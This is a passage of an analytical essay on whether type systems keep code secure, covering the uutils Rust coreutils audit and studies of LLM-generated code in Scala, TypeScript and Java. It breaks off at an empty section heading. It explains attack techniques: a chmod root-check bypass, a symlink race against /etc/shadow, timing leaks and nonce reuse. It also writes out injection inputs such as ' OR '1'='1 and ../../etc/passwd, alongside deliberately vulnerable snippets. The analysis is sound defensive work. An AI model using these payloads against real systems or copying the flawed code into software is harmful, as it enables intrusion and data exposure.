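A recent audit shows what can go wrong in code written in a language with a strong type system. Canonical, the company behind the Linux distribution Ubuntu, decided to replace standard commands such as `cp` and `rm` with uutils, a rewrite in Rust, and hired the security firm Zellic to audit the code. Ubuntu's *An update on rust-coreutils* reports 113 issues, and 44 of them received entries in the public vulnerability database, according to *uutils coreutils CVEs* (Funk, 2026). *Bugs Rust Won't Catch*, an essay by the Rust consultancy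 corrode, notes that the list contains no buffer overflows and no uses of freed memory. Over a comparable period, the GNU project's C versions had several memory errors.

Some vulnerabilities come from checking the wrong rule, and moving the same check into a type does not fix them. The command `chmod` changes file permissions, and it has an option that should prevent it from changing the whole system at once. The Rust version compared the path with `/`, the top of the file system. The path `/../` leads to the same place but does not match, so the check let it through. A smart constructor for a `NotRoot` type that used this comparison would also have accepted `/../`, so a `NotRoot` value could still have referred to the root.

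An algebraic data type also can't ensure that a parser chooses the case the user meant. GNU's `kill` command reads `-1` as signal number 1 and then requires a process ID. The Rust version read it as process -1, which on Linux means every process the user is allowed to signal. If a parser turned the command line into a sealed set of cases, both readings would be valid values of the type.

One of the worst bugs came from doing two steps in the wrong order. The command `chroot` confines a program to one folder and can run it as a chosen user. The Rust version entered the folder first and looked up the user's name afterwards. That lookup could load code from inside the folder, so an attacker who had put a file there could run code with full administrator rights. GNU's version looks up the name first. A type could enforce this order if the function that enters the folder required the user's numeric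 id, which the program gets only from the lookup. But the programmer would have to know about the danger to write such a type.

Business logic raises the same difficulty with rules specific to one organisation, such as how many discounts a customer may combine. *Design Flaws in AI Generated Code* (Stiefel, 2026) describes a small study in which researchers gave an AI assistant 20 tasks on a fictional web platform, and 15 of the results had a design flaw. When asked for a registration page, the assistant made every new user an administrator. A sealed trait with the cases `Member` and `Admin` would allow this because both are legitimate roles.

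Types could still have caught part of the problem. Twelve of the 20 results failed to reuse the platform's existing controls, such as its role checks and audit log. In Python web code these are often optional additions to a function, so a programmer or model can leave them out. If the platform's functions required a permit or an audit record as an argument, a type checker could report the omission. Someone would have to design those functions first, and the assistant would have to use them instead of writing its own. Scanners that search code for known bad patterns do little better than types with business rules. Help Net Security's *AI coding agents keep repeating decade-old security mistakes* notes that they don't trace, for example, whether a game's server checks the price of an item a player unlocks.

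### Data that skips the constructor

Some ways of loading data bypass smart constructors. Java's built-in serialization, for example, converts objects to bytes and back. It rebuilds an object of an ordinary serializable class without calling that class's constructor, so any checks there do not run. Scala's case classes, including `Admin` from the session example, support this mechanism by default. A program that rebuilds sessions from bytes sent by the visitor would accept an `Admin` that the visitor had made up. Deserialization of untrusted data (CWE-502) is 15th in the ranking, with 11 exploited vulnerabilities.

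TypeScript has a less visible version of this problem. The expression `JSON.parse(text) as Order` makes the compiler treat data from the network as an `Order` without checking that it is one. Database records can also bring in bad values if another program wrote them or if they predate the current rules. The remedy in each case is to parse the data where it enters the program, as King recommends.

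### Changes outside the program

The largest group of bugs in the uutils audit came from files that can change between two operations. The `install` command deleted an old file and then created a new one under the same name. corrode describes how an attacker with access to the folder could, between the two steps, place a symbolic link there to `/etc/shadow`, where Linux keeps password hashes. The command would then follow the link and overwrite that file. Security engineers call this a time-of-check to time-of-use race, because something changes after the program checks it and before the program uses it.

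Rust has a type for paths, but a path is only a name, and the operating system looks it up again on every call. A type that records "this path is safe" can therefore be out of date by the next call. An open file handle is better evidence, because it keeps referring to the same file even if someone changes the name. The repaired `install` uses a setting that refuses to create the file if anything already exists at that path. For other operations, the essay recommends opening the parent folder once and working from that handle. Funk notes that Canonical kept the GNU versions of `cp`, `mv` and `rm` in Ubuntu 26.04 because of these races. Even a good interface protects only the code that uses it. GitLab's *CVE-2026-35362* (2026) records that uutils had a module to prevent such races, but its developers had enabled it only for Linux, which left macOS and FreeBSD exposed.

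Web servers face a similar race when they fetch addresses that users supply. In server-side request forgery (CWE-918), an attacker asks the server to fetch a page from a private machine that only the server can reach. SecurityWeek reports that all five of Tenzai's agents introduced this vulnerability. To prevent it, a `PublicUrl` type should carry the numeric address that the program checked was public, and the program has to connect to that address. If the type carried only the name, an attacker who controls the name could point it at a private machine after the check.

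### Dependencies, timing and resources

In most languages, a function's type signature gives only what it accepts and returns, so a library function that turns a `String` into `SafeHtml` could also send the string to a stranger's server. A commenter on Ubuntu's announcement counted 523 entries in the dependency list of uutils and asked whether anyone had audited them. An Ubuntu developer described a tool that records which packages went into a program, so that users can check for versions with known flaws, but the tool does not find new flaws.

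A program can also leak a secret through its running time. Suppose a server compares a visitor's login token, 32 characters that are each one of 16 symbols, with the correct one. An ordinary comparison stops at the first wrong character, so a guess with more correct characters at the start takes slightly longer. Someone who could measure this reliably would need at most 16 × 32 = 512 guesses instead of up to 16³², although network noise means repeating each guess many times. Timing leaks can pass every unit test, according to the security company Endor Labs, and they also pass type checking. A comparison that always takes the same time fixes the leak. A type can steer programmers towards this comparison by hiding the ordinary one, but in Scala, `==` works on almost any pair of values by default, even those with opaque types.

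Types can enforce some resource limits. A refined type can cap a user name at 100 characters, but the compiler does not track how many requests arrive or how much memory they use together. CWE-770, which covers programs that set no such limits, is last in the ranking. Crashes can also take a service down, and strongly typed code can crash easily. The Rust version of `sort` crashed when a list of files contained a name that was not valid text, because its code called `expect`, which ends the program if a conversion fails. Language models also write code that calls `expect` instead of handling the error.

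### Encryption that compiles

Types let a compiler check that the inputs to encryption code have the exact sizes required, but the main danger in that code depends on what the program did earlier. AES-256-GCM and ChaCha20-Poly1305, two widely used encryption methods, each take a secret key and a nonce ("number used once"), which need not be secret but must be different for every message encrypted under the same key.

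The reason is simple arithmetic. The method uses the key and the nonce to generate a stream of random-looking bits, S, and combines it with the message m by XOR (written ⊕), which flips each bit of the message where S has a 1. If a program encrypts two messages with the same key and nonce, it uses the same S both times:

c₁ = m₁ ⊕ S and c₂ = m₂ ⊕ S, so c₁ ⊕ c₂ = m₁ ⊕ m₂

An eavesdropper can combine the two encrypted messages to cancel S without knowing the key. If they know one message, they can work out the other. With AES-GCM, nonce reuse also lets an attacker forge messages.

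Elsayed, Fulton and Yang (2026), in *An Empirical Security Evaluation of LLM-Generated Cryptographic Rust Code*, had Gemini 2.5 Pro, GPT-4o and DeepSeek Coder, all now old models, write encryption programs in Rust. Each model wrote 10 programs for every combination of two encryption methods and four prompts, for a total of 240. Only 56 (23.3%) compiled. The most common single reason for failure, in 41% of the 184 rejected programs, was a call to a function that does not exist. Type errors and similar mismatches together accounted for another 47%.

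The researchers then searched the 56 compiled programs for security problems with an analyser they had written. It flagged 32 of them (57%), all of which contained careless error handling. One also reused a nonce, and another had its key written into the source code. The other 30 had no flaw except the error handling, so the analyser found serious flaws in 2 of the 56 programs, or 3.6%.

The careless error handling involves `Result`, the algebraic data type a Rust program receives when it decrypts a message. It holds either the message or an error. The compiler makes the programmer deal with both possibilities, but it accepts a call to `.unwrap()` or `.expect()`, which extracts the message or crashes if there was an error. An attacker can then crash a server by sending it a damaged message. The same call does little harm in a short demonstration program that decrypts only its own message,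 and the prompts asked for complete programs of about that kind. The 57% therefore mostly measures a bad habit rather than broken encryption.

Even when one prompt explicitly told the models not to use `.unwrap()` on cryptographic operations, at least 13 of the 17 resulting programs that compiled used it or `.expect()`. That minimum follows from the study's other numbers. None of DeepSeek's 20 compiled programs used the shortcut or came from this prompt, so all 32 flagged programs were among the other two models' 36, and at most four of the 17 could have avoided it.

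The two serious flaws passed the compiler because every value had the right type. The hard-coded key was an English phrase 32 characters long, the size the method requires. In the program that reused a nonce, the code generated the nonce from a secure source of randomness but then passed it to the encryption function twice. Elsayed and colleagues point out that Rust's type system checks the sizes of keys and nonces but not whether nonces are unique. CodeQL, a widely used code scanner, found neither flaw, and its only two alerts were false alarms.

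The percentages are rough. The researchers set the models to give their most likely answer each time, so the 10 programs for each combination were probably close to copies of each other. Consistent with this, DeepSeek's 20 compiled programs all came from two combinations in which every program compiled. The analyser also missed 4 of 18 known flaws in a separate test, so the compiled programs may contain flaws that it did not report.

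### A nonce that works only once

A stricter library would have prevented the nonce reuse. The encryption function in that program borrowed the nonce, so the program could use it again. The Rust cryptography library ring takes ownership of the nonce instead, and its `Nonce` type is deliberately not cloneable.

```rust
let nonce = Nonce::assume_unique_for_key(bytes);

key.seal_in_place_append_tag(nonce, Aad::empty(), &mut first)?;
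key.seal_in_place_append_tag(nonce, Aad::empty(), &mut second)?;
// the second call does not compile: the first one took the nonce
```

This prevents a program from using one `Nonce` value twice, but two values can contain the same 12 bytes. The code below compiles and has the same flaw as the model's program.

```rust
let n1 = Nonce::assume_unique_for_key(bytes);
let n2 = Nonce::assume_unique_for_key(bytes);
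```

As the function's name indicates, the library assumes that the bytes are unique, and the programmer has to make sure they are. A programmer or model could get rid of the compiler error in the first example by switching to the second, without making sure the bytes are unique.

The library also offers a design that takes this decision away from most of the code. It recommends keys that come with a sequence of nonces, and describes the simpler key used above, called `LessSafeKey`, as an option for programs that cannot reasonably use them. A program that encrypts with a sequence-bound key does not supply a nonce at all, because the key takes the next one from its sequence. The compiler also prevents copying such a key, since ring's developers wanted to rule out two copies that would produce the same nonces. The danger is now confined to the code that generates the sequence, but the compiler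 does not check that code for repeats:

```rust
struct AlwaysZero;

impl NonceSequence for AlwaysZero {
    fn advance(&mut self) -> Result<Nonce, Unspecified> {
        Ok(Nonce::assume_unique_for_key([0; 12]))
    }
}
```

This sequence returns the same nonce for every message, and it compiles. According to ring's documentation, whoever writes a sequence must ensure that it never repeats a nonce. Replacing the constant with a counter fixes the problem within a single run. But if the program stores its key on disk and starts the counter from zero after a restart, it will reuse the first nonces. Two servers that share a key and each count from zero will also use the same nonces. The compiler can't rule out these repeats because it examines one program at a time, and whether a nonce is unique depends on every message encrypted with that key.

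## How do models use types when nobody asks them to?

Language models asked for ordinary code in a typed language usually write something that compiles, but there is little sign that they use types to rule out bad values. The evidence is indirect, because the studies below measured coding style, escape hatches and vulnerability rates, and none reports how often a model defined its own sealed trait or refined type.

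### Scala that reads like Java

In *Perish or Flourish?*, Lang, Lang and colleagues (2026) tested three OpenAI models on Haskell, OCaml and Scala, with Java for comparison. Haskell and OCaml are functional languages, in which programs mostly compute new values instead of changing old ones. Scala allows both styles. Their test suite, FPEval, has 721 puzzles from LeetCode, a website where programmers practise for job interviews. For each puzzle, a model received a description and a template with the function's signature, and wrote one solution.

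The table gives the results for GPT-5, the newest of the three models, and compares its style with GPT-4o's. Of the programs that passed every test, "clean" is the share in which the language's style checkers found no problems.

| Language | GPT-5 passed all tests | GPT-5 did not compile | Clean, GPT-4o | Clean, GPT-5 |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Haskell | 42.3% | 24.3% | 46% | 45% |
| OCaml | 52.2% | 13.7% | 61% | 44% |
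| Scala | 58.4% | 9.3% | 77% | 57% |
| Java | 61.1% | 4.6% | 63% | 51% |

Nobody can attack a program that does not compile, so the errors in the third column take time to fix but do not threaten security. Lang and colleagues suggest that models make more of these errors in Haskell and OCaml because their training data contained less code in those languages.

GPT-5 wrote slightly more clean Scala programs than GPT-4o, about 240 against 215, but they made up a smaller share of its solutions, 57% against 77%. Lang and colleagues compare this fall to reward hacking, where a model learns to pass the tests at the expense of everything else. A simpler explanation may be that GPT-5 solved 420 of the Scala puzzles and GPT-4o only 280. The extra puzzles were probably harder and needed longer programs, which give a style checker more to flag.

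The most common complaint about the Scala code was the use of `return`, with 236 instances. Scala programmers rarely write it, because a function's last expression is already its result. Using it is a habit from Java and other imperative languages, in which a program is a series of commands that change variables.

```scala
def totalImperative(prices: List[Int]): Int =
  var sum = 0
  for p <- prices do sum += p
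  return sum

def totalFunctional(prices: List[Int]): Int =
  prices.sum
```

Lang and colleagues searched all the generated code for such patterns and found them in 94% of GPT-5's Scala programs, 88% of its Haskell programs and 80% of its OCaml programs. The keyword search was broad. In Scala it counted any mutable variable or explicit loop, and in Haskell it counted some `let` definitions, which are a normal part of the language.

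Both functions above have the same types and the same result, so the imperative one is no less secure. The habit does harm when it reaches the values that carry a guarantee. Suppose a model wrote the `CanRead` permit from the account example with a changeable field:

```scala
final class CanRead private[Accounts] (var accountId: Int)

permit.accountId = 8   // compiles, after a check on account 7
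```

Any code that holds a permit for account 7 could now read account 8. A model can't make this mistake in LeetCode puzzles, since they have no accounts or attackers. Their templates also fix the types of the input and output, much as the signatures did in the study of 32 models described earlier.

FPEval measures style, not whether models use algebraic data types or write secure code. Its only result related to data types is that the Haskell compiler warned of missing cases in some programs' pattern matches. The researchers also turned off GPT-5's reasoning to make the comparison with older models fair, so the model could not work through a problem before answering. GPT-5 is now more than a year old.

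In a further experiment, the researchers gave each model the complaints about its code and written advice on fixing common problems. The share of GPT-5's correct OCaml programs that were clean rose from 44% to 91%, but many of the OCaml complaints were about trivia such as redundant parentheses. In Scala the share rose only from 57% to 60%. The baseline in the TypePilot experiment, which the next section describes, comes closest to measuring models' default behaviour on Scala code with real security requirements.

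### More `any`, and more of everything else

TypeScript is JavaScript with static types added, and it makes type checking unusually easy to bypass. The compiler doesn't check how a program uses a value of type `any`, so the value can go anywhere.

```ts
type SafeHtml = string & { readonly brand: "SafeHtml" };
declare function send(page: SafeHtml): void;

const fromUrl: string = location.hash;
send(fromUrl);              // does not compile

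const loose: any = fromUrl;
send(loose);                // compiles
```

The result of `loose.trim()` is also `any`, as is nearly everything else the program computes by calling methods on `loose` or reading its fields.

*Mining Type Constructs Using Patterns in AI-Generated Code* (Lee, Ul Hassan and Hindle, 2026) counts how often coding agents and people add `any` to real projects. The study began with a public collection of TypeScript pull requests (proposed changes that a project's maintainers can accept or reject), 33,596 by agents and 5,080 by people. A keyword search, followed by a filter based on GPT-4o, narrowed these to the requests that dealt with types, 545 by agents and 269 by people.

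The agents added `any` 2.16 times per request on average, and the people 0.24 times. The gap is ninefold, but the effect size is modest. Cohen's d, the difference between two averages divided by the typical spread of the data, was 0.32, and researchers conventionally call 0.2 small and 0.5 medium. The spread was therefore about (2.16 − 0.24) / 0.32 = 6 uses per request. With averages this low, a spread of 6 means that a minority of requests added a great many uses, while most added few or none.

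Lee and colleagues report no adjustment for the size of the requests. An agent that changed nine times as many lines as a person would add nine times as many `any`s at the same rate per line, so the study can't distinguish the effect of larger requests from carelessness about types. It also covers only the small share of requests that dealt with types, under 2% of those from agents, so the averages don't describe agents' TypeScript in general.

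Among the agents, Cursor added about 2.5 `any`s for each one it removed and OpenAI's Codex added about 2.3, while GitHub Copilot removed more than it added.

Agents also used more of TypeScript's advanced type features. The average request from a person contained 2.66 different ones, against 5.50 for Codex and 6.74 for Claude Code, with the other agents in between. The effect size was large, at 1.45. However, the count includes features that bypass the compiler's checks, such as type assertions, which are TypeScript's casts, and non-null assertions, where a programmer adds `!` to a value to stop the compiler checking whether it is missing. Request size could also inflate the count. The figures do suggest that agents know the type system well and freely use both its protections and the features that bypass them. Project settings can forbid some of these bypasses, as a later section explains.

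Maintainers accepted 45.8% of the agents' requests and 25.3% of the people's, which Lee and colleagues take as a hint that type problems may slip through review. But maintainers also rejected 42.6% of the agents' requests and only 2.6% of the people's, so most of the human requests had presumably received no decision. Among requests with a decision, maintainers accepted those from people more often, at about 91% compared with 52% for those from agents.

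### Are typed languages safer by default?

A strict compiler might still catch models' mistakes when they use types carelessly. GitHub's *Why AI is pushing developers toward typed languages* makes this case, calling type systems a safety net for code that developers did not write themselves. It cites a finding that 94% of the compilation errors in model-written code were failed type checks. That figure doesn't measure how many vulnerabilities remain in the programs that do compile.

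Veracode, a company that sells code scanners, regularly tests the security of code written by language models. It gives each model 80 functions in Java, JavaScript, C# and Python, each with a part missing and a comment describing what that part should do. Each function can be completed securely or with one of four weaknesses: SQL injection, cross-site scripting, log injection or weak cryptography. Veracode's scanner then checks the result. The *Spring 2026 GenAI Code Security Update* (2026) is Veracode's latest report with a figure for all four languages. In the *2026 GenAI Code Security Report* (2026), published in July, Java scored 30%, almost the same as in spring, although it had improved more clearly than any other language over the years. Python scored 63%, according to eSecurity Planet's *Veracode Finds AI-Generated Code Still Struggles With Security*.

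Improta, Liguori and Cotroneo (2026) made a much larger comparison in *What is the Difference Between Me and You?*. They collected 787,562 functions in Python, Java and C that people had written for open-source projects, had three models write each function again from its signature and description, and ran the security scanner Semgrep on every version. In the table, the column of secure tasks shows Veracode's spring result, and higher is better. The last two columns come from Improta and colleagues, and lower is better.

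| Language | Static types | Tasks completed securely | Human functions flagged | Model functions flagged |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Python | no | 62% | 5.6% | 5.7–8.0% |
| JavaScript | no | 57% | – | – |
| C# | yes | 58% | – | – |
| Java | yes | 29% | 3.0% | 6.1–19.6% |
| C | yes, with easy casts | – | 8.9% | 6.7–9.4% |

Neither set of results favours the typed languages. In Veracode's tests, C# did about as well as JavaScript, and Java did half as well as Python. Veracode attributes Java's result to the large amount of old Java code that models learned from, some of it written before programmers recognised SQL injection as a danger. This is plausible, but the company has not tested it. Veracode also used only twenty tasks per language and doesn't run the programs to see whether they work.

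The study by Improta and colleagues includes a human baseline. Scanners have different rules for different languages, so it would be risky to use the table to compare the safety of Java and Python, but within each language the same rules apply to people and models. Semgrep flagged the models' Java functions between 2 and 6.5 times as often as the human ones, and their Python functions at most 1.4 times as often, even though the models' functions were only about half as long. Java's type checker did not keep the models close to the human standard.

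Many of the extra Java findings have little to do with types. DeepSeek-Coder had the worst result, and 62% of its findings were for code that logged sensitive information or left debugging code in place. Path traversal is more relevant because a file name in ordinary Java is a `String`, so `../../etc/passwd` passes the type checker. Semgrep found path traversal 14 times in the human Java code, 2,886 times in ChatGPT's and 3,738 times in DeepSeek-Coder's, but only 4 times in that of the third model, Qwen2.5-Coder.

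All three models are old. Improta and colleagues also tested the newer Claude Opus 4.8 on 600 tasks, and Semgrep flagged its code on about a third of them. That rate is not comparable with those in the table because the researchers deliberately chose tasks that had caused trouble before.

Working attacks are better evidence than a scanner's warnings. In *BaxBench*, Vero, Mündler and colleagues (2025) asked models to build 28 small server applications in each of 14 web frameworks, across six languages. They tested whether each application worked and then attacked it. The tests and attacks reach the running server over the network, so they are the same for every language. OpenAI's o1 did better in popular languages such as Python and JavaScript than in Rust, which has the strictest type checker of the six. Among the programs that worked, those in less popular frameworks, such as Rust's Actix,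 were also more often vulnerable. Actix was the only Rust framework in the test, and o1 is an old model, but the pattern suggests that a model's familiarity with a language matters more than the language's type checker.

Newer models still had trouble with this kind of task. *AutoBaxBuilder* (von Arx, Mündler and colleagues, 2025) adds 40 applications for the same 14 frameworks. Claude Sonnet 4.5 produced a working program 83% of the time, and one that also withstood the attacks 36% of the time.

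One study does favour static types. Schreiber and Tippe (2025), in *Security Vulnerabilities in AI-Generated Code*, searched GitHub in February 2024 for files with comments crediting an AI tool, and scanned them with CodeQL. Among files crediting ChatGPT, CodeQL found a weakness in 16.2% of Python files, 8.7% of JavaScript files and 2.5% of TypeScript files. CodeQL uses the same checks for JavaScript and TypeScript, so the gap between those two is less likely to come from the scanner. But the developers chose the language themselves, and those who chose TypeScript may have had more experience, different projects or stricter reviewers. Schreiber and Tippe say they could not rule out the effects of experience, project complexity and review.

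### A string is a string

A typed language helps so little by default because most programs pass text around as plain strings. This Java code looks up a user by name:

```java
String query = "SELECT * FROM users WHERE name = '" + name + "'";
statement.executeQuery(query);
```

Like the greeting page that joined plain strings, this code has correct types whatever the visitor enters. But if the name is `' OR '1'='1`, the database returns every user. The equivalent Python program has the same flaw.

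Ordinary types help with numbers. If the code looked up an account with `"... WHERE id = " + id`, and `id` were an `int`, the query would be safe from injection, because an `int` can only hold a whole number. This protection doesn't extend to names, comments, file paths or log messages. Python also doesn't enforce type annotations when the program runs, so a parameter declared as `id: int` could still contain text.

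The same problem explains much of the difference between weaknesses in Veracode's results. In Veracode's July report, models passed 83% of the SQL injection tasks and 87% of the cryptography tasks, but only 15% of the cross-site scripting tasks and 12% of the log injection tasks. Veracode's original *GenAI Code Security Report* (2025) explains that a query with placeholders is the right choice whether or not its inputs come from an attacker, so a model can always write one without knowing where they come from. But to escape correctly, a model has to know which variables hold raw input and which are already safe, and the single function it sees in each task doesn't contain that information.

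A separate type for cleaned log messages, as suggested earlier, would show in the function's signature whether a message has been cleaned, and the model could read it there too. Veracode's tasks had no such types, and a model that fills in a function's body cannot add them to the code that calls it.

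## What changes when the prompt asks for these types?

When a prompt asks for algebraic data types, sealed traits and refined types, models write safer Scala, and the improvement is much larger when they also review and rewrite their first draft. *TypePilot* (Sternfeld, Kucharavy and Dolamic, 2025) provides the most direct evidence. With a plain prompt, 1 of 15 programs that handled untrusted text was fully safe from injection. A single prompt asking for safe, well-typed code raised the count to 6, and a three-step process of drafting, reviewing and rewriting raised it to 14. The experiment is small and does not separate the effect of the types from that of the review.

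### The three conditions

The plain prompt describes the model as a Scala code generator and gives it the task, without mentioning security. The robust prompt adds a request to pay attention to safety and robustness and to use Scala's type system where needed, listing "ADTs, refined types, traits, sealed traits" as examples. The model still answers in one call.

TypePilot is the name of the three-step process. The same model handles each step in a separate call:

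1. **Draft.** The model gets the plain prompt and writes a program.
2. **Review.** The model gets the task and the draft, and describes potential vulnerabilities without writing any code.
3. **Revision.** The model gets the task, the draft and the list of vulnerabilities. The prompt tells it to fix them by using Scala's type system, and gives the same four examples as the robust prompt.

In one of the paper's tasks, Qwen2.5-Coder had to write a function that takes a page name and returns that page's address on `https://example.com`. The draft appended the name to the address. In the review, Qwen listed five problems, including that the function accepted empty names and that a space in a name would produce an invalid address. The revision defined a sealed trait for page names and encoded special characters.

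One of the five problems Qwen listed was a false alarm. The supposed risk was that someone could supply `https://malicious.com` as the page name to send visitors to that site, but browsers treat everything after `https://example.com/` as a page on example.com. TypePilot does not check the list of problems before the revision.

### Tasks and grading

Five of the tasks involve injection. Each program takes text that an attacker might control and uses it to greet a user in HTML, list comments in HTML, search for a file with a shell command, ping another computer (send it a test message) or build the redirect address described above.

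The other four tasks calculate an average age, a Fibonacci number, a matrix product and a matrix convolution, which slides a small grid of weights called a kernel over a larger grid. The danger in these tasks is an input that makes no sense, such as a negative age or an empty matrix. The researchers checked ten such edge cases across the four tasks.

The published results cover three code models: Qwen2.5-Coder (32 billion parameters), CodeLlama (70 billion) and DeepSeek-Coder (33 billion). Sternfeld and colleagues tested each model on nine tasks under three conditions and graded the resulting 81 programs by hand. For each injection task, they recorded whether the program compiled and worked, and whether it was robust, partly robust or not robust to injection.

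### What the grades add up to

The workshop version of the paper, by Sternfeld and colleagues, gives individual grades without totals. Adding them up produces this table.

| Result | Plain prompt | Robust prompt | TypePilot |
|---|---|---|---|
| Injection programs that worked | 15 of 15 | 12 of 15 | 13 of 15 |
| Injection programs fully safe | 1 of 15 | 6 of 15 | 14 of 15 |
| Both working and fully safe | 1 of 15 | 5 of 15 | 12 of 15 |
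| Edge cases handled in calculations | 6 of 30 | 10 of 30 | 22 of 30 |

The plain column also shows how these models write Scala by default. Every injection program worked, and all but Qwen's ping program had some weakness to injection.

With the robust prompt, nine injection programs were not fully safe, though three of them were partly protected. With TypePilot, only Qwen's redirect function was not fully safe, and it was partly protected. The difference was largest for the file search, where no model produced a safe version with the robust prompt and all three did with TypePilot. Sternfeld and colleagues explain that the robust prompt typically led models to rearrange a shell command without validating its input.

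The calculations followed a similar pattern. All nine average-age programs handled an empty list, but only two handled negative ages, and both came from TypePilot. The robust prompt added six edge-case checks but lost two that the plain programs had, including Qwen's check for empty matrices in matrix multiplication. TypePilot's programs passed every check that the plain or robust programs passed.

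The experiment is small, but the gap between the robust prompt and TypePilot is probably not luck. In eight of the 15 comparisons on the injection tasks, TypePilot's program was fully safe and the robust prompt's was not. The reverse never happened. If both methods were equally good and the comparisons were independent, the probability that all eight would favour TypePilot would be (1/2)⁸, or 1 in 256. The same models and tasks recur, so the comparisons are not fully independent and the real probability is somewhat higher.

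### Differences between models, and broken programs

In the next table, each cell gives the counts for the plain prompt, the robust prompt and TypePilot, in that order.

| Model | Injection programs fully safe, of 5 | Edge cases handled, of 10 |
|---|---|---|
| Qwen2.5-Coder | 1, 2, 4 | 3, 6, 10 |
| CodeLlama | 0, 2, 5 | 2, 1, 6 |
| DeepSeek-Coder | 0, 2, 5 | 1, 3, 6 |

Qwen handled every edge case with TypePilot. CodeLlama, the largest of the three, handled fewer with the robust prompt than with the plain one. CodeLlama's convolution function gave wrong answers for ordinary matrices in all three conditions. The TypePilot version still got credit for three edge cases, though a check for empty matrices is of little use in a function that gets ordinary ones wrong. Without that function, the counts are 6, 10 and 19 of 26.

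TypePilot's revisions sometimes broke programs. Its drafts come from the same prompt as the plain programs, all 15 of which worked on the injection tasks. After revision, DeepSeek-Coder's greeting program failed and CodeLlama's comment list program worked only partly. The robust prompt did slightly worse, with two programs that failed and one that worked only partly.

The grades combine compiling and working in one mark, so they don't show whether a failed program was rejected by the compiler or ran and gave wrong output. This matters because a compile error is obvious and a model can often fix it if it gets the error message, though TypePilot never compiles the code between steps.

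The full TypePilot process took about 45 seconds per task on four Nvidia A100 data-centre GPUs. By the paper's estimates, the single-call prompts emitted a little over a third as much carbon. Sternfeld and colleagues intend TypePilot for software such as aircraft controls and medical devices, where correctness matters more than speed.

### Types or a second look?

Sternfeld and colleagues credit Scala's type system with the improvement. Testing that would require varying the type instruction and the review separately, but they ran only three of the four combinations. The table shows fully safe injection programs.

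| | One call | Draft, review and revision |
|---|---|---|
| No mention of types | 1 of 15 | not tested |
| Types mentioned | 6 of 15 | 14 of 15 |

Both prompts in the bottom row mention types, so the rise from 6 to 14 must come from the review and revision, or from their combination with the type instruction. In the left column, the robust prompt adds a general request for safety as well as the mention of types, so the rise from 1 to 6 can't be attributed to types alone. The missing cell would show the effect of a review when the prompt doesn't mention types. At 45 seconds per task, running it for all nine tasks and three models would take about 20 minutes of computing, plus the grading.

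An earlier study of Python comes close to filling the gap. *Prompting Techniques for Secure Code Generation* (Tony, Díaz Ferreyra and colleagues, 2024) tested Recursive Criticism and Improvement, in which a model writes code, looks for security problems in it and then improves it. This is almost the same as TypePilot, except that the last prompt doesn't mention types. The researchers gave 150 security-relevant tasks to three OpenAI models and counted weaknesses with Bandit, a scanner for Python.

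| Prompt given to GPT-4 | Weaknesses per program |
|---|---|
| Plain | 0.756 |
| Asks for "secure" code | 0.662 |
| Gives the model the role of a security expert | 0.666 |
| Asks it to prevent the top CWE weaknesses | 0.455 |
| Review and improvement | 0.265 |

The review loop cut GPT-4's weaknesses by 65%, while adding the word "secure" to the prompt cut them by 12%. The reviewed programs averaged 40 lines, against 17 with the plain prompt, so the reduction didn't come from shorter or emptier programs. The review loop helped older models less, cutting weaknesses by 28% for GPT-3.5 and 25% for GPT-3. GPT-3 did better with a prompt that spelled out the precautions for each task's particular weakness. A plausible reason is that a review helps only if the model can find its own mistakes.

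The study shows that a review can bring a large improvement without any mention of types, so the review could well account for much of TypePilot's gain. However, a scanner's count of weaknesses in Python can't be compared numerically with hand grades of Scala programs.

Sternfeld and colleagues note that CodeLlama sometimes dealt with vulnerabilities outside the type system, yet all five of its injection programs were fully safe with TypePilot. So at least some of the safety probably came from ordinary checks that the model added after seeing a list of problems.

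Sternfeld and colleagues also compared TypePilot with Self-Planning, a technique that Jiang and colleagues introduced in 2024. The model writes a plan for the task, then code that follows it. The prompts also told the model to consider security. TypePilot did better on both kinds of task, and the difference was largest for Qwen. The plans often mentioned security in general terms, but the code rarely contained a concrete protection. Sternfeld and colleagues conclude that telling a model to think about safety is not enough. That seems right, but Self-Planning lacks both the type instruction and the review of finished code, so this comparison doesn't separate their effects.

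Sternfeld and colleagues examined Qwen's attention weights, which record how strongly a model draws on each earlier piece of text as it produces the next. When Qwen revised the redirect function, the weights were high on the listed vulnerabilities and on the instruction to use typed constructs such as sealed traits. With the robust prompt, the safety wording affected mainly the explanation Qwen wrote after the code. This suggests that Qwen used the type instruction, but the analysis covers one task and one layer of one model, and they call it preliminary. It can't show what Qwen would have written without the instruction.

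### What the robust prompt contained

It is not certain whether the robust prompt named the types. The paper's description of the method includes the list of examples, but the transcript of Qwen's run on the redirect task shows a shorter version that mentions the Scala type system but gives no examples. Elsewhere the paper describes the robust prompt as a general security reminder, modelled on one used by Vero and colleagues in BaxBench.

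In that transcript, Qwen rejected some bad page names but kept page names as plain strings instead of defining a new type. If the other runs also used the shorter prompt, the 6 of 15 result came from a vague request for type safety, and a single prompt that named sealed traits and refined types might have done better. According to the paper, TypePilot's revision prompt does name these types, so the two conditions may also differ in this way.

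### What the grades can and cannot measure

Each of the nine tasks consists of a single function, graded on its own, so the experiment measures whether models add the right checks. It doesn't test the main benefit of types, which is catching later mistakes in the rest of a program. For example, a greeting function that escapes its own input gets the same mark as one that accepts only `SafeHtml`.

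Types also create work that isn't visible in a single function. If a revised function takes a `ValidFilename` instead of a `String`, all code that calls it has to change. Sternfeld and colleagues acknowledge that larger codebases would be harder, since a model would need to know about types and rules defined in other files. They suggest describing each relevant object in the prompt, but did not test this.

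The grading is another weakness. TypePilot's designers also graded its output, and the paper mentions no second grader and no attempt to hide which prompt produced each program. The paper doesn't define "partly robust". At least one grade looks too harsh. All three plain file-search programs were marked as failing on injection, but the one that the paper prints passes `find` a list of arguments instead of building a shell command. The overall pattern holds without the file-search task, with 1, 6 and 11 safe programs out of 12.

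The paper's description of the experiment does not match its results in two places. It says that six models ran in every condition, but the results for these tasks cover only the three coding models and omit Llama 3, a version of DeepSeek-R1 and Qwen3. If the missing models did worse, the published figures overstate how well the method works, but the paper does not include the data needed to check. The task list also includes a factorial function with no reported results and leaves out the average-age function, which does have results. The researchers say that they put their prompts and generated code in a public repository, so somebody else could regrade the programs.

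The last problem is the age of the models. DeepSeek-Coder dates from 2023, CodeLlama from January 2024 and Qwen2.5-Coder from November 2024. Current models write much better code and can plan and check their work before answering, so they might do part of the review without a separate prompt. The robust prompt might then come closer to TypePilot, or the plain prompt might already produce safe code on tasks this small. No published study seems to have repeated the experiment on newer models.

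### Security prompts in other studies

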